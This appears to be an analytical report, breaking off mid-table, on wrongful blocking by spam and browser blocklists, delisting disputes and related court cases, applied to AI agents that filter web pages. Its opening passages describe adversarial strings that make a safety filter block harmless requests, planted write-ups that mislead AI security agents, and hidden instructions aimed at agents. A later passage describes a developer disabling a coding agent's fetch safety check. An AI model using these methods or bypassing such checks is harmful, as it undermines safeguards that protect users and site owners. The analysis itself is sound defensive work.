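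Attackers could try to fool the detector instead of the agent. In *LLM Safeguard is a Double-Edged Sword*, Zhang, Xiong and Mao (2024) looked for strings that make a safety filter reject harmless requests. Strings of about 30 characters made Llama Guard 3, a model that screens requests to chatbots, block more than 97% of harmless requests. The attack required access to the filter's internal parameters and to the template that held the user's request, and they did not test it on web pages. If a similar string worked in a product review, agents would report the shop because of a few odd words that its owner would have no reason to delete.

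A list operator might use another AI agent to investigate the reports, but planted evidence can mislead that agent too. *Poisoned Playbooks* (2026) found that AI security agents adopted false technical claims from planted write-ups, each of which took 30 to 60 minutes to produce. The write-ups worked best when the agents had trouble checking their claims, and one could be enough where there was little other evidence. A false accusation against a large retailer would compete with thousands of other pages, but an attacker's write-up might be most of what the agent finds about a small camera shop that opened last month.

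## Case reports of wrongful blocking

Lists can also block harmless sources even when no attacker has fed them false evidence. Mail and browser lists have done so for more than twenty years, usually because of errors, neglect or shared addresses, but sometimes as a deliberate policy.

### A single slash at Google

On 31 January 2009, Google marked nearly every search result with the warning "This site may harm your computer". According to the Los Angeles Times' *Google mistakenly warns that search results ‘may harm your computer’* (2009), this lasted from 6:30 to 7:25 a.m. California time, and anyone who clicked on a result got an error message. The SANS Internet Storm Center (2009) reported the same fault on international versions of the search engine.

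Google explained that someone had mistakenly added "/" to its list of sites that install malicious software, and that the slash matched every web address. Engineers restored the old list, and a typical user saw the warnings for about 40 minutes.

Google released its list updates in stages, which can limit the damage from a bad one, but here the stages followed each other too quickly. The warnings reached the first users at 6:27 and the last at 6:40, but the correction didn't reach anyone until 7:10. With an hour between the first stage and the rest, most users would never have seen the warnings, but they would also have waited an extra hour for protection against each new malicious site. An automatic test might avoid that delay by comparing each update with a few thousand well-known harmless sites and holding it back if many of them matched.

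### Lists that nobody maintained

A DNS blocklist can block all mail after it closes. Many mail servers treat any address record as a listing, so whoever controls the list's domain can list the whole internet with a wildcard, a DNS record that answers for every possible name. Some operators have done this on purpose.

Many mail administrators used relays.osirusoft.com, a combination of several blocklists that Joe Jared started in 2001. According to *Status of relays.osirusoft.com* (2025), he shut the list down in August 2003 after attackers flooded his servers with traffic. In *relays.osirusoft.com*, Welty (2003) told other network operators on 26 August that the list now returned 127.0.0.2 for everything, and that anyone still using it wouldn't receive his message.

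According to Jared's notice on the OsiruSoft website, still online in May 2008, he blocked all mail to servers using the list to get their administrators' attention. The servers were still sending his network an enormous number of queries, and he thought administrators would ignore the problem if they got no response. Some may not have known they used the list, because SpamAssassin seems to have queried it automatically.

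Guilmette had earlier forced users off ORBS, a list that had closed. In 2001, he announced a change to a name server for its domain, calling the change a "more than compelling incentive" to find another list.

The Open Relay Database (ORDB) closed on 18 December 2006, and queries to it timed out for the next 15 months. On 25 March 2008, it began blocklisting every IP address, as Siles (2008) reported the next day in *ORDB.org blocklisting all IP addresses*. Many spam filters still used ORDB by default, and Siles's own mail provider took about a day to fix the problem.

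Senders got an error message that named ORDB and said it had closed, but this didn't always lead them to the server that had blocked their mail. In *need ordb.org removed from Red Hat MX mail servers* (2008), a Dell employee asked the software company Red Hat to stop using the list, because the error message named one of Red Hat's servers. But another organisation's server had rejected the email further along its route, and Red Hat wasn't using the list.

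A list can also block everything by accident. SpamCannibal's operator abandoned the list, and its domain expired in 2018. Domain squatters bought the name and, as they usually do, set up a wildcard DNS record, which made the list match every address. Word to the Wise, an email delivery consultancy, notes that few mail servers relied on this list. It warns that a filter that never queries the standard test addresses can lose all mail to a dead list if it blocks on any match, or send some good mail to the spam folder if it only counts a match toward a score. Similarly, an agent that gives listed sources less weight would suffer less from a dead list than one that blocks them.

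Two later closures went better. Proofpoint, the security company that owned SORBS, shut it down on 5 June 2024 and confirmed that it no longer held any reputation data, according to *Status of dnsbl.sorbs.net* (2024). The operators of the German list NiXSpam emptied it on 16 January 2025. heise online's *Spam filter* reports that they planned to keep its servers running for at least six more months so that queries would get a quick "not listed" instead of timing out.

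An empty blocklist blocks nobody, but it also catches no spam, and its users may not notice. When the SORBS lists came back empty, the monitoring service HetrixTools (2024) initially marked addresses as delisted, and learned the real reason two days later. Soini (2025, *Use of nixspam which got shutdown 2025-01-16 (Fedora all + epel all)*) found that a SpamAssassin add-on for Fedora Linux was still querying NiXSpam a month after it closed. An agent with an emptied blocklist would likewise treat every site it checked as clean.

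Someone also has to keep paying for the old domain, or its next owner will control the answers to queries sent there. In *SORBS is gone*, Sullivan (2024) announced that the SORBS domain would move to servers reserved for decommissioned lists. heise online's *Blocked out* reports that spammers were trying to acquire the domain.

A working list can cause a total block when its operator changes the rules. In February 2025, Spamhaus began sending an error code to people who used its free lists through the network of Hetzner, a German hosting company. Some servers misread that code as a listing. Later that year, Spamhaus warned users of Korea Telecom's network of a similar risk. It announced these changes in advance, but an agent's owner might not know which lists the agent depends on or whose network it uses to reach them.

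### One address, many users

Many people can share one IP address because IPv4, the older and still common numbering system, has too few addresses. Some internet providers put many customers behind one address at the same time, while others reassign addresses from one customer to another. In both cases, a list that blocks an address for one person's spam also blocks people who had nothing to do with it.

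Ramanathan, Hossain and colleagues (2020), in *Quantifying the Impact of Blocklisting in the Age of Address Reuse*, measured how often 151 public blocklists might wrongly block people because an address was shared or reassigned. To find shared addresses, they contacted users of the file-sharing network BitTorrent. If two or more BitTorrent programs answered from the same address at the same time, several users were probably sharing it. To find reassigned addresses, they used 16 months of records from measuring devices that volunteers had connected to their own networks. If a device changed address at least eight times, and did so about daily, they counted its whole block of 256 addresses as reassigned.

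They then followed the blocklists for 83 days in 2019 and 2020.

| | All listed addresses | Several users at once | Reassigned about daily |
|---|---|---|---|
| Addresses found | 2.2 million | 29,700 | 22,700 |
| Average time on a list | 9 days | 10 days | 3 days |
| Removed within two days | 42% | 60% | 77.5% |

About 60% of the lists contained at least one address shared by several users at once, and 53% contained at least one reassigned address. Shared and reassigned addresses together made up about 2% of all listed addresses. The true share is probably higher, because the method for detecting shared addresses misses anyone who doesn't use BitTorrent, and the method for detecting reassigned ones covers mainly Europe and North America.

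The quick removals in the last column protect people less than they seem to. If an address changes hands every day but stays listed for three days, the block probably affects later customers for most of that time, not the person who caused the listing.

The most crowded address had at least 78 users, but the researchers detected only two users at most shared addresses. Some shared addresses stayed on a list for all 44 days of the second observation period, so the real maximum may be longer.

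Being on a blocklist harms someone only if a network acts on the list. Ramanathan and colleagues surveyed 65 network operators, and 59% said they used blocklists to block traffic directly. Of the 34 who answered questions about shared addresses, 76% thought that address reassignment made blocklists inaccurate. Many operators evidently use blocklists despite knowing about this problem.

In October 2025, Cloudflare, a company that delivers and protects websites, published *One IP address, many users*, in which Giotsas and Fayed trained a program to recognise addresses that internet providers share among many customers. Websites that use Cloudflare limited the number of requests from these addresses three times as often as from other addresses, although the median share of requests that looked automated was nearly the same, at 4.8% for shared addresses and 4.7% for the rest.

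Rate limiting is milder than blocking, and it often depends on the number of requests rather than any record of abuse. A hundred ordinary people behind one address can easily look like one very busy visitor. The finding therefore shows that address-based rules treat people who share an address worse, but it doesn't measure the effect of reputation lists.

The burden falls unevenly because organisations in North America and Europe received most of the large address blocks decades ago. Giotsas and Fayed found that providers in much of Africa and in Central and Southeast Asia rely heavily on sharing addresses, and that African providers put more customers behind each one. An agent running on a user's own computer in these regions connects from the same shared address, so websites may slow or refuse it for reasons unrelated to the user.

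Websites also share IP addresses, which matters more for a filter that decides what an agent may read. Cloudflare's *The unintended consequences of blocking IP addresses* (2022) reports that fewer than ten IP addresses were enough to reach about 51 million of 255 million domain names. In August 2022, Austrian internet providers blocked 11 of Cloudflare's addresses under a court order meant to stop 14 websites accused of copyright infringement. The block made thousands of unrelated sites unreachable in Austria for two days. Although it came from a court order, an agent that filtered websites by IP address could make the same mistake with a single entry in its reputation list.

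A bad record can also pass to a new owner. In 2016, a network operator who had bought a block of 1,024 addresses complained on a mailing list that more than 400 of them were on SORBS (the discussion includes Hodger (2016), *We bought a /22 and +400 IPs are listed in SORBS*). The reverse happens when attackers buy lapsed domains for their good records. A filter that clears a source's good record when ownership changes should probably clear a bad one too, though spammers could exploit this by selling addresses to themselves.

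### Immich and the warnings on new sites

In October 2025, Google Safe Browsing marked all the websites under immich.cloud as dangerous (Rasmussen, 2025, *Google flags Immich sites as dangerous*). The domain belongs to the team behind Immich, a free photo-storage program that people install on their own servers.

1. Google's report named several preview pages, temporary copies of the program that the team uses to test changes. It said they tried to trick visitors into installing unwanted software or revealing personal information.
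2. The warning covered the whole domain, including internal tools that the report hadn't named.
3. The team had to create a Google account to request a review. It explained that the pages were its own product, and Google removed the warning a day or two later.
4. The team created another preview page, and Google flagged the domain again.

Rasmussen guesses that Google's crawler finds the preview links on GitHub and mistakes the pages for imitations of Immich's demonstration site. This is plausible, because phishing detectors are designed to flag familiar login pages at unfamiliar addresses. Some users who ran their own copies of Immich also reported warnings. Any popular program that people host themselves could have this problem, since each legitimate installation looks like a copy of the others.

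The successful review corrected one verdict but did not address its cause. Rasmussen planned to move the previews to a separate domain, immich.build, so that a new warning wouldn't affect anything else. It's FOSS's *Safe Browsing Flags Open Source Photo App Immich Web URLs as Dangerous* later reported that the team had moved away from its .cloud addresses. Google warns site owners that its lists may misidentify a safe site.

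Separate lists can also disagree about the same site. In July 2026, a developer on Apple's support forum reported that Safari was flagging two websites as fraudulent a week after their registration. In the same discussion, *Possible increase in false positive “Fraudulent Website Warning” detections in Safari (2026)*, a second developer described a warning on another new site. That developer moved the product to a fresh domain and redirected the old address to it, and Safari flagged that domain too within hours. Google's lists flagged none of the four domains.

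The developers then noticed that all four sites were on servers run by Aeza, a Russian hosting company under sanctions since 2025. One concluded that the only solution was to change hosts and buy new domains. Apple may distrust the host, but the sites were also new, and the redirect could explain the last warning. The developers are also the only source for the claim that the sites were harmless. Apple's reasons aren't public, so a site owner in this position can't tell what to change.

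### Blocking innocent customers on purpose

Some early spam lists deliberately blocked a provider's innocent customers, a practice called escalation. If a provider kept hosting a spammer, the list's operator extended the listing from the spammer's address to neighbouring ones, and might eventually list the provider's whole range. SORBS had a separate list for this, escalations.dnsbl.sorbs.net.

The argument for escalation is that a spammer pays the provider, so the provider has little reason to act on complaints. Listing only the spammer's address achieves little, because the provider can assign a new one. If the provider's other customers can't send mail either, they will complain or leave, and keeping the spammer will cost the provider more than dropping it. On this view, harming a few thousand people for a few days could prevent years of spam to everyone else.

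The main objection is that these customers did nothing wrong. They may not know that a spammer uses the same provider, and they may have a long contract or no other provider to choose. People who use the list also lose wanted mail, possibly without knowing that its operator blocks more than spammers. The operator suffers almost none of this harm, so little stops a listing from becoming too broad or being used to settle a grudge.

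ORBS, which listed servers that would forward mail for anyone, included all 65,536 addresses in one provider's range, although only about 70 were known to belong to such servers. The operator of ORBS said that the provider had demanded the listing and told him to stop testing its machines. Other network engineers who looked up the range could not learn of this dispute from the entry.

Broad policies hurt the lists' users too. In March 2000, Jason Gunthorpe of the Linux project Debian calculated that ORBS would have blocked 3,970 of 40,236 connections to the project's mail system, or about 10%. He thought most of these carried legitimate mail. ORBS listed servers that spammers could use, whether or not they had, so many of these blocks would probably have been correct under its rules but false positives for the people waiting for the mail.

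If operators of a list for agents escalated against web hosts that ignore reports of hostile pages, the pressure would fall mainly on small hosts, because a list that blocked every page on Google Sites would lose many of its own users. Escalation also works only if the innocent customers know they are being blocked, since a shop that doesn't know agents are skipping it has no reason to complain to its host.

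### When an agent skips the page

People often discover wrongful blocks by seeing them. The SANS Internet Storm Center learned of Google's 2009 error because words such as "harmful" and "malware" suddenly became popular on Twitter. Immich's developers saw the red warning page, and their users complained about it.

If a filter wrongly blocks a small camera shop, an agent can find another shop and give the user an answer that looks complete. The blocked shop sees only that few agents visit, which could just as easily mean that few people want its cameras. Neither the user nor the shop has a reason to report an error, so the shop may stay on the blocklist indefinitely. Cloudflare says that even it can't routinely see when someone blocks one of its addresses, and a small shop has far less data. Small error rates add up over many sources, so an agent that doesn't mention blocked sources could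 hide many wrongful blocks.

The documented cases in agent products so far come mainly from coding agents, whose users tend to read error messages. One developer using Claude Code with another company's model found that its WebFetch tool would not open deepseek.com or docs.bigmodel.cn, the websites of two Chinese AI companies. The error message was that the tool could not verify that the domain was safe. The cause was the check with Anthropic's server that precedes each fetch, though the developer first thought that Chinese websites were blocking the tool. Both sites opened normally after the developer turned the check off.

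The refusals most likely happened because the program couldn't reach Anthropic's server, not because of the sites' records. Companies can cause the same failure with their own firewalls. Anthropic's *Enterprise network configuration* explains that WebFetch still contacts api.anthropic.com for the check when a company runs the model through Amazon, Google or Microsoft. An administrator who has moved everything else to one of these providers could easily block that address as unnecessary.

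Unlike Safe Browsing's local procedure, Claude Code blocks a site when the check gets no answer. This is safer, but an outage then blocks every site that needs the check, which can lead users to remove the protection altogether. The developer's solution was to skip the check for all sites, including any that Anthropic had actually listed. A message that clearly distinguished a listed site from an unavailable list would let users fix the connection instead.

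A refusal is also worse if the agent has few ways to find a replacement page. In October 2025, Claude Code hid its web search tool from users who ran it through Amazon's Bedrock service, according to *Inside Claude Code's Web Tools*. If one of those users' agents was refused a page, it couldn't search for another with its built-in tools.

Allowlists cause more predictable wrongful blocks. In *Please add WebFetchSafe tool*, a user of the coding agent Cursor describes asking it to make an app work like one described in a particular article. The agent can't read the article because its cloud environment permits connections only to approved domains. The user knows about this block because they supplied the link. If the agent had searched for articles itself, it could have used one from an approved site without mentioning the others.

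New and small sites seem most at risk. The Safari reports concern sites a week or two old, and in the 2008 email study, more of the lists' mistakes involved small senders. There is much less evidence about whether a site's language matters. The two sites that Claude Code refused were Chinese, but the failed check would have stopped an English site too. Cloudflare's regional figures cover people trying to visit websites, not the websites published in those regions. A filter could easily be less accurate for a language that its operator's reviewers don't read, but these cases don't test that.

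Case reports also don't show how often wrongful blocks happen, because an unknown shop with Immich's problem might leave no public record of it. Counting complaints would be especially misleading for agents, because a product that hid its refusals would receive fewer complaints than one that reported them. To measure the rate, a company could log every source its agent refused, draw a random sample, and have people who read each site's language check whether the refusal was wrong. It would also need to count the harmless sites that the agent opened.

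## Delisting disputes and court rulings

The owner of a wrongly blocked site has to persuade whoever runs the list to remove the entry, usually by submitting a web form and waiting a few days. Some owners have sued when this failed, and their cases give some idea of the legal disputes AI companies might face over the lists their agents use.

### Getting off a list

Li and colleagues' HADES study also compared how the 29 email blocklist providers remove entries. Most delete an entry automatically after a while and let the owner of the address or domain apply for earlier removal. The owner typically has to prove ownership and explain the abuse. A sender framed by an attacker may have no abuse to explain, unlike an owner who has cleaned up a hacked server.

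Six providers make early removal difficult.

| Provider | Obstacle |
|---|---|
| Gbudb | Offers no early removal |
| Justspam | The sender must first be off 14 other popular lists |
| S5h | The request must come from the listed IP address |
| Uceprotect, Spfbl and Backscatterer | A fee, which can reach $500 |

S5h's rule stops spammers who relay mail through someone else's server from clearing that server's record. It also stops customers of a shared mail host from clearing the host's record, because they don't own the server.

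Li and colleagues found 307,244 domains whose rejection messages named a blocklist. At most 1.5% of them used any of these six lists, while over 90% used Spamhaus. A sender stuck on one of the six would therefore lose little mail, but a shop on a major AI company's list might lose every visit from that company's agents.

Lewis and Sergeant say an operator should publish its criteria for adding and removing entries and follow them. It should answer a removal request within two days, and must do so within seven unless it has already told the applicant that more discussion won't help. It must not use its own list to block emails asking for removal. Removal conditions should relate to the reasons for the listing. Justspam's rule seems inconsistent with this unless the other lists were part of its reason. These are recommendations from a research group, so an operator can ignore them.

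They also advise most operators against restricting who may request removal, because checking requesters takes too much effort. They think many lists do better with a "no questions asked" policy, under which the operator removes an entry immediately for anyone who asks but can limit repeated requests. This policy corrects mistakes quickly and keeps many disputes from escalating.

Removing entries on request would be riskier for a list of pages with hostile instructions. If the operator crawls the web once a month, a dishonest site could ask for removal and then have up to a month to attack agents. With cloaking, it could stay off the list for much longer. The operator could check the page before removing the entry, using a visitor that looks like a real agent.

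The guidelines protect a list's users more than the people on it. Some operators have listed people merely for insulting them, and Lewis and Sergeant see nothing inherently wrong with this if the operator discloses it. A mail administrator who dislikes the practice can choose another list. The guidelines don't apply to private lists, though they suggest private operators might use them as a starting point. An AI company's list is usually private, and a blocked shop can't choose which agents its customers use.

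### Paying for removal

Lewis and Sergeant do not object to charging a list's users, but they say that operators must not charge for removal or for faster handling. They write that such fees come "perilously close to notions of extortion, blackmail", and that even an unjustified accusation of this kind damages the reputation of blocklists in general. They recommend that mail administrators avoid lists that charge such fees.

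Operators who charge for delisting reply that the fee only speeds up removal. Uceprotect, for example, says that its entries expire free of charge seven days after the last abuse. A fee may also discourage spammers from repeatedly delisting the same address, and reviewing requests costs money.

This is a reasonable defence if a week's delay does little harm, but a small business that can't send invoices for a week may feel it has to pay. The fee also gives the operator a reason to list too many sources. Uceprotect lists address ranges and entire networks as well as single addresses, so many of the people affected may have sent no spam. An operator could reduce the conflict of interest by refunding the fee when a listing turns out to be wrong.

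A removal fee has the same weakness as a fee for new identities. A well-funded attacker can afford $500 to get a useful domain delisted, but the owner of a new camera shop might give up.

### e360 v. Spamhaus

e360 Insight's suit against Spamhaus, the best-known lawsuit over a spam list, lasted five years and ended with an award of three dollars. e360 sent advertising emails for other companies. In December 2003, Spamhaus added e360 and its operator, David Linhardt, to its Register of Known Spam Operations, which listed people and businesses that at least three internet providers had cut off for breaking their rules. e360 said that no provider had ever cut it off, and that Spamhaus also listed its business partners and refused to remove them until they stopped working with e360.

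Spamhaus (2011), by contrast, says that e360 hid behind shell companies and sent millions of spam messages, many through hijacked computers.

e360 sued in Illinois in 2006, claiming defamation and interference with its existing and future business. Judge Kenneth Ripple (2007), in *E360 Insight v. the Spamhaus Project*, describes how Spamhaus came to lose without a trial. Spamhaus, a British organisation, first filed an answer that raised 14 defences, including that the court had no jurisdiction over it. A month later, its lawyer told the trial judge, Charles Kocoras, that Spamhaus wanted to withdraw the answer and do nothing more. "Do they want to lose?" the judge asked.

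Kocoras entered a default against Spamhaus because it did not defend itself. On 13 September 2006, he awarded e360 $11,715,000. The figure came entirely from a sworn statement by Linhardt, who put the lost contracts at $2,465,000 and the company's lost value at $9,250,000 or more. Kocoras also ordered Spamhaus to stop listing e360 unless it could prove that e360 had broken US law, and to post a notice saying that e360 was not a spammer.

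e360 soon complained that Spamhaus was ignoring the order, and asked the court to have Spamhaus's domain name suspended. In the Northern District of Illinois' *e360 Insight vs. The Spamhaus Project* (2006), Kocoras refused. The companies that would have had to suspend the domain were not parties to the case, and the suspension would have stopped all of Spamhaus's lawful activities there too. Mail servers query Spamhaus's lists under that domain, so a dispute over one sender could have disabled the lists for everyone.

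By then, Spamhaus had appealed. In 2007, the Seventh Circuit, a US federal appeals court, upheld the default because Spamhaus had knowingly given up its defences, but it cancelled the damages and the order. Linhardt had given a total for lost profits without showing that those profits had ever been likely. The court found the order too broad because the default established only that the listing was false when Spamhaus first published it, and Spamhaus might later find new evidence and list e360 again. The court also saw no basis for replacing Spamhaus's criteria, which concerned providers' rules, with a test based on US law.

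e360 now had only to prove how much it had lost. Judge David Hamilton (2011), in *e360 Insight, et al v. Spamhaus Project*, recounts how it failed. Linhardt repeatedly missed appointments to testify before the trial, and e360 named 16 new witnesses at a late stage. Its estimate of the damage also kept changing.

| Stage | Amount claimed | Amount awarded |
|---|---|---|
| Default judgment, 2006 | $11,715,000 | $11,715,000 |
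| Exchange of evidence | $135,173,577 | |
| Week before the trial | $122,271,346 | |
| Final argument | $30,000,000 | |
| Trial judgment, June 2010 | | $27,002 |
| Second appeal, September 2011 | | $3 |

Kocoras excluded the late witnesses and found most of Linhardt's testimony unreliable, partly because of these changes. He accepted only that e360 had lost three customers who together paid about $27,000 a month. He awarded one month's payments, plus a token dollar for each of the two other claims. According to CircleID (2010), he did not issue another order against Spamhaus.

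The appeals court further reduced the award to one dollar for each of the three claims. The $27,000 was based on revenue, but damages should replace lost profit. e360 owed royalties whenever its emails brought in money, and it had given no evidence of how much it would have kept.

### What the case left open

The case shows how hard it can be for a listed sender to prove its losses. Linhardt estimated the losses by multiplying the average revenue per email by the number of emails he believed providers had blocked. Spamhaus could hardly supply a better number, because it blocked no mail itself and gave the list away without recording who used it.

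The case decided very little about the listing because Spamhaus defaulted, which meant the courts had to treat the "spammer" label as false without examining the evidence. They never considered whether the label was a fact or an opinion, or whether a US court would have had jurisdiction over a British list operator that kept objecting to it. According to CircleID, Spamhaus also had a good defence under Section 230, the US law that protects filtering, but the court could not test it because of procedural problems.

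According to Spamhaus, e360 also sued the internet provider Comcast for blocking its mail and lost, and the judge in that case called e360 a spammer.

### The 2013 attack on Spamhaus

Some opponents of a listing have attacked the list's operator instead of suing. In March 2013, attackers flooded Spamhaus with traffic after it listed addresses belonging to CyberBunker, a Dutch hosting company that accepted almost any customer. They sent small queries to thousands of misconfigured DNS servers and forged Spamhaus's address as the sender, so the servers sent their much larger replies to Spamhaus. The traffic reportedly peaked at about 300 gigabits per second, a record at the time. A man speaking for CyberBunker argued that nobody had given Spamhaus the authority to decide what belonged on the internet.

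The flood knocked Spamhaus's website offline until Cloudflare absorbed the traffic. The blocklists kept working because many volunteer organisations ran copies of them. A smaller operator might have had to give up, as the owner of relays.osirusoft.com did after a similar attack in 2003. Even an attack that leaves the blocklists running can hurt innocent senders, who may need the website to request removal. A year before the Spamhaus attack, Lewis and Sergeant had advised operators to prepare another means of contact for this situation.

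### Section 230 and *Zango*

Section 230(c)(2) of the US Communications Decency Act protects filtering in two ways. Part A covers an online service that in good faith restricts access to material it considers obscene, harassing or "otherwise objectionable". Part B covers giving others the technical means to restrict such material, and doesn't mention good faith.

Courts first read this protection very broadly. Zango, which gave people access to videos, games and other downloads if they agreed to see advertisements, sued the security company Kaspersky for blocking its software. The Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, ruled that the law protected Kaspersky as a distributor of security software, according to FindLaw's summary of *Zango, Inc. v. Kaspersky Lab, Inc* (2009). Judge Pamela Rymer wrote the opinion.

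The law firm Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Restricts Immunity for Filtering Objectionable Content* describes the protection that security companies had before the Enigma ruling as "near limitless". Raymond Fisher, one of the *Zango* judges, had already warned that a company might block content "for anticompetitive purposes or merely at its malicious whim" (quoted in Tushnet, 2019, *Enigma Software Group USA, LLC v. Malwarebytes, Inc*).

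### *Enigma v. Malwarebytes*

The next major case involved Enigma and Malwarebytes, direct competitors that both sell programs that find and remove malicious software. The facts that follow are Enigma's allegations, as summarised in the Northern District of California's *Order Denying Defendant's Renewed Motion to Dismiss Second Amended Complaint*.

For eight years, Malwarebytes's products did not flag Enigma's. On 5 October 2016, Malwarebytes changed its criteria for "potentially unwanted programs", and its products began labelling two of Enigma's programs as unwanted and as threats, and disabling them. A user could restore a program manually, but Malwarebytes's software would disable it again the next time the user tried to open it. Enigma sued two days after the change.

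In December, during a dispute with its competitor Malwarebytes over two programs, Enigma released an installer that disabled Malwarebytes's software. Malwarebytes's products then began blocking every address under enigmasoftware.com as a "Malicious Website".

The case has since gone back and forth between the trial court and the Ninth Circuit.

1. The trial court dismissed it because Section 230 protected Malwarebytes, as it had protected Kaspersky.
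2. In the Ninth Circuit's *Enigma Software v. Malwarebytes* (2019), the appeals court revived it. "Otherwise objectionable" does not include software that a company objects to for anticompetitive reasons, and Enigma had alleged enough to suggest such a motive. The Supreme Court declined to hear an appeal.
3. The trial court dismissed the case again, this time because it considered the labels to be opinions, which can't be proved false.
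4. In 2023, the Ninth Circuit mostly reversed that decision too. As Tushnet (2023), in *The fact/opinion divide*, explains, it treated "malicious" and "threat" as statements of fact that Enigma could challenge. "Potentially unwanted program" was too vague.
5. In June 2024, the trial court refused to dismiss the remaining claims.

The June 2024 decision allowed the case to continue but did not find that Malwarebytes had done anything wrong. At this stage, a court assumes that the plaintiff's factual allegations are true and asks whether they would be enough to win. Nearly eight years after Enigma sued, no court had decided whether its programs deserved the labels or why Malwarebytes had applied them.

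The main remaining claim is false advertising, so the trial court also had to consider whether a warning inside a program could be an advertisement. It found this plausible because Enigma alleged that the labels appeared during a free trial, next to an upgrade button.

Goldman strongly disagrees in *This Case Keeps Wrecking Internet Law*. He points out that the same warning also appears after a customer has paid, when there is nothing left to sell. Under the court's reasoning, a label could count as advertising before the customer upgrades and as something else afterward. He expects that most security companies will now avoid flagging one another's products, even when a product deserves it. The dissenting judge in 2023 had a similar worry and said the ruling sent security companies "a chilling message", according to *9th Circ. Revives Lanham Act Suit As Dissent Raises Red Flag* (Eslinger,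 2023).

The concern is serious because fake security programs are an old scam. If a company can be sued for years over a correct warning, it may decide the warning isn't worth the cost. But a company with unlimited protection could disable a competitor's product on millions of computers and never have to explain why. The 2019 rule seems right in principle, but it helps an honest company less than it should, because a competitor needs only plausible allegations of a bad motive to get past an early request for dismissal.

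### Notice and appeal in Europe

European law gives some people a right to reasons or corrections, but it fits blocklists poorly. The EU's Digital Services Act requires a hosting company to explain why it removed a customer's content for breaking the law or its terms. Larger online platforms must also offer a free way to complain. These duties are owed to people who use the service, such as a shop whose web host deletes its page. A shop on a blocklist usually has no relationship with the list's operator, so it probably can't rely on the same rules.

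Data protection law may help an individual more. The EU's General Data Protection Regulation lets people demand the correction of inaccurate personal data about them, which would normally include an entry that names a person, as the Spamhaus register named Linhardt. The right offers little to most businesses, because an entry for a large retailer's domain, for example, would not be personal data.

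### What agent companies might face

None of these cases involved an AI agent, so applying them to one is guesswork. Lewis and Sergeant describe a blocklist as its operator's opinion and say that the mail administrator who uses it is responsible for the consequences. An AI company that builds its own private list into its agent is both operator and user, so unlike Spamhaus, it can't pass that responsibility to anyone else.

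Section 230 might protect such a company, but the protection could depend on which part applies. If users or administrators can choose whether to apply the list, the company looks more like Kaspersky, which supplied a filtering tool. If the agent refuses pages under rules the user can't see or change, a court might treat the blocking as the company's own act and ask whether the company acted in good faith.

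The wording of a refusal could also matter. After the 2023 ruling, calling a shop "malicious" is riskier than calling it a "low-trust source", but the vaguer label leaves the owner unable to tell what to fix. A precise and true statement might be better for both sides. If a competitor plants hidden instructions in a review on a camera shop's site, an agent could accurately say "This page contains hidden instructions to AI systems" without falsely calling the shop malicious.

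An agent that skips a shop without comment makes no statement about it, so the shop would probably find it harder to claim defamation or false advertising. If the shop found out, it could still claim that the company behind the agent had interfered with its business. The law may therefore give companies a reason to hide refusals, although mistaken refusals are hardest to correct when they are hidden.

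The greatest legal risk probably comes from blocking competitors. Companies that build agents may also sell search, advertising, software or cloud services, so many of the sites their agents visit belong to rivals. Even a failed connection can look like a deliberate block to outsiders. Such a failure is probably why Claude Code refused the websites of two Chinese AI companies. A company could more easily answer suspicions of deliberate blocking if it published its criteria, recorded the reason for each entry and reviewed entries for competitors separately. Enigma bases its complaint partly on the sudden change of criteria and on a later request for an explanation, which Malwarebytes allegedly never answered.

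Even with a good claim, a small shop would have to prove its losses. An AI company might have a log of every page its agent refused, which would give the shop better evidence than e360 had, but the shop would still have to show how much profit those visits would have produced. As an invented example, suppose an agent refused 10,000 visits to a camera shop, and 2% of them would have led to the sale of a $500 camera at a profit of $40. The shop would have lost $100,000 in revenue, but under the rule in *e360* it could claim only the $8,000 in lost profit, which would cover only a small part of the cost of a lawsuit.

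## Who should run shared reputation data

A small shop that can't afford to sue depends on the list's operator to correct its own mistakes. In email, that operator is usually Spamhaus. For the HADES study, Li and colleagues searched 190 million bounce messages that Coremail received in 2022 and 2023. Blocklist names appeared in bounces from 307,244 domains. Of these, 288,514 used Spamhaus and 15,825 used SpamCop, the second most common.

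The paper gives Spamhaus's share as about 90% and the share of domains relying on a single list as nearly 95%, but its own counts work out to 94% and 96%. The 90% figure seems to come from counting a domain once for each list it uses.

The estimated share relying on a single list is probably too high, because a mail server that checks several lists in turn may stop at the first match and name only that list in its bounce message. The data also omit any list that never blocked Coremail's customers. But a direct test also found that Spamhaus has great influence. When the researchers got their own server onto Spamhaus's list and wrote to 15 popular email services, seven rejected more than 99% of the messages.

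### Why one list comes to dominate

One reason is that few people choose a list themselves. Microsoft's Outlook service hosts 185,996 of the domains, about 61%, so Microsoft's choice of Spamhaus applies to all of them. However, at least 84% of the remaining domains also used Spamhaus, so many other administrators and hosting companies made the same choice.

Administrators had good reasons to choose popular lists. Spamtraps and staff cost about the same whether a list has a thousand users or a million, so a popular list can afford better ones. A second list adds little if it catches the same spam, and it can add many errors, as SORBS did in the 2008 email study. Lewis and Sergeant advise administrators to ask whether sites like their own use a list and what their peers think of it. This advice is sensible for each administrator, but it favours lists that are already popular.

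Many browsers also rely on a single provider. According to the reference article *Google Safe Browsing*, Chrome, Safari, Firefox, Brave and Vivaldi all use Google's list, which was in use on more than 3 billion devices by September 2017.

Sharing one list makes each error more serious, even if it doesn't make errors more common. Suppose five companies each run a fifth of all agents, and each list wrongly blocks 0.5% of shops. If the companies share one list, a shop has a 0.5% chance of losing every agent's visits. If they keep separate lists whose errors are independent, it has about a 2.5% chance of being on at least one, but would usually lose only a fifth of its visits. The average loss is the same, but a small business is more likely to survive the smaller loss, although it may have to appeal to several companies instead of one.

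A dominant operator also has more power over the sources it lists. A sender that only SpamCop blocks can still reach about 95% of the domains in the Coremail data, so it can ignore unreasonable demands from SpamCop, but a sender on Spamhaus's list has to meet Spamhaus's conditions.

### How existing arrangements compare

Spamhaus, Google and Microsoft each decide for themselves what to list, while PhishTank lets volunteers vote. In other arrangements, companies share evidence and each company decides what to block. Members of the Anti-Phishing Working Group (APWG), an industry association, exchange reports of phishing pages. The Global Signal Exchange, which Google, the Global Anti-Scam Alliance and the DNS Research Federation announced in October 2024, is used to share similar reports about scams.

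Governments run lists too. CERT Polska, Poland's national computer emergency team, publishes a list of fraudulent domains that telecoms companies can block. A 2023 law defines which sites belong on it and lets a domain's owner file an objection with the telecoms regulator.

| Arrangement | Who decides | What outsiders can see | Who hears an appeal | Who pays | Likely source of pressure |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
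| Spamhaus | Its researchers and software | Criteria, and whether a source is listed | Spamhaus | Large users of the data | Listed senders who sue or attack |
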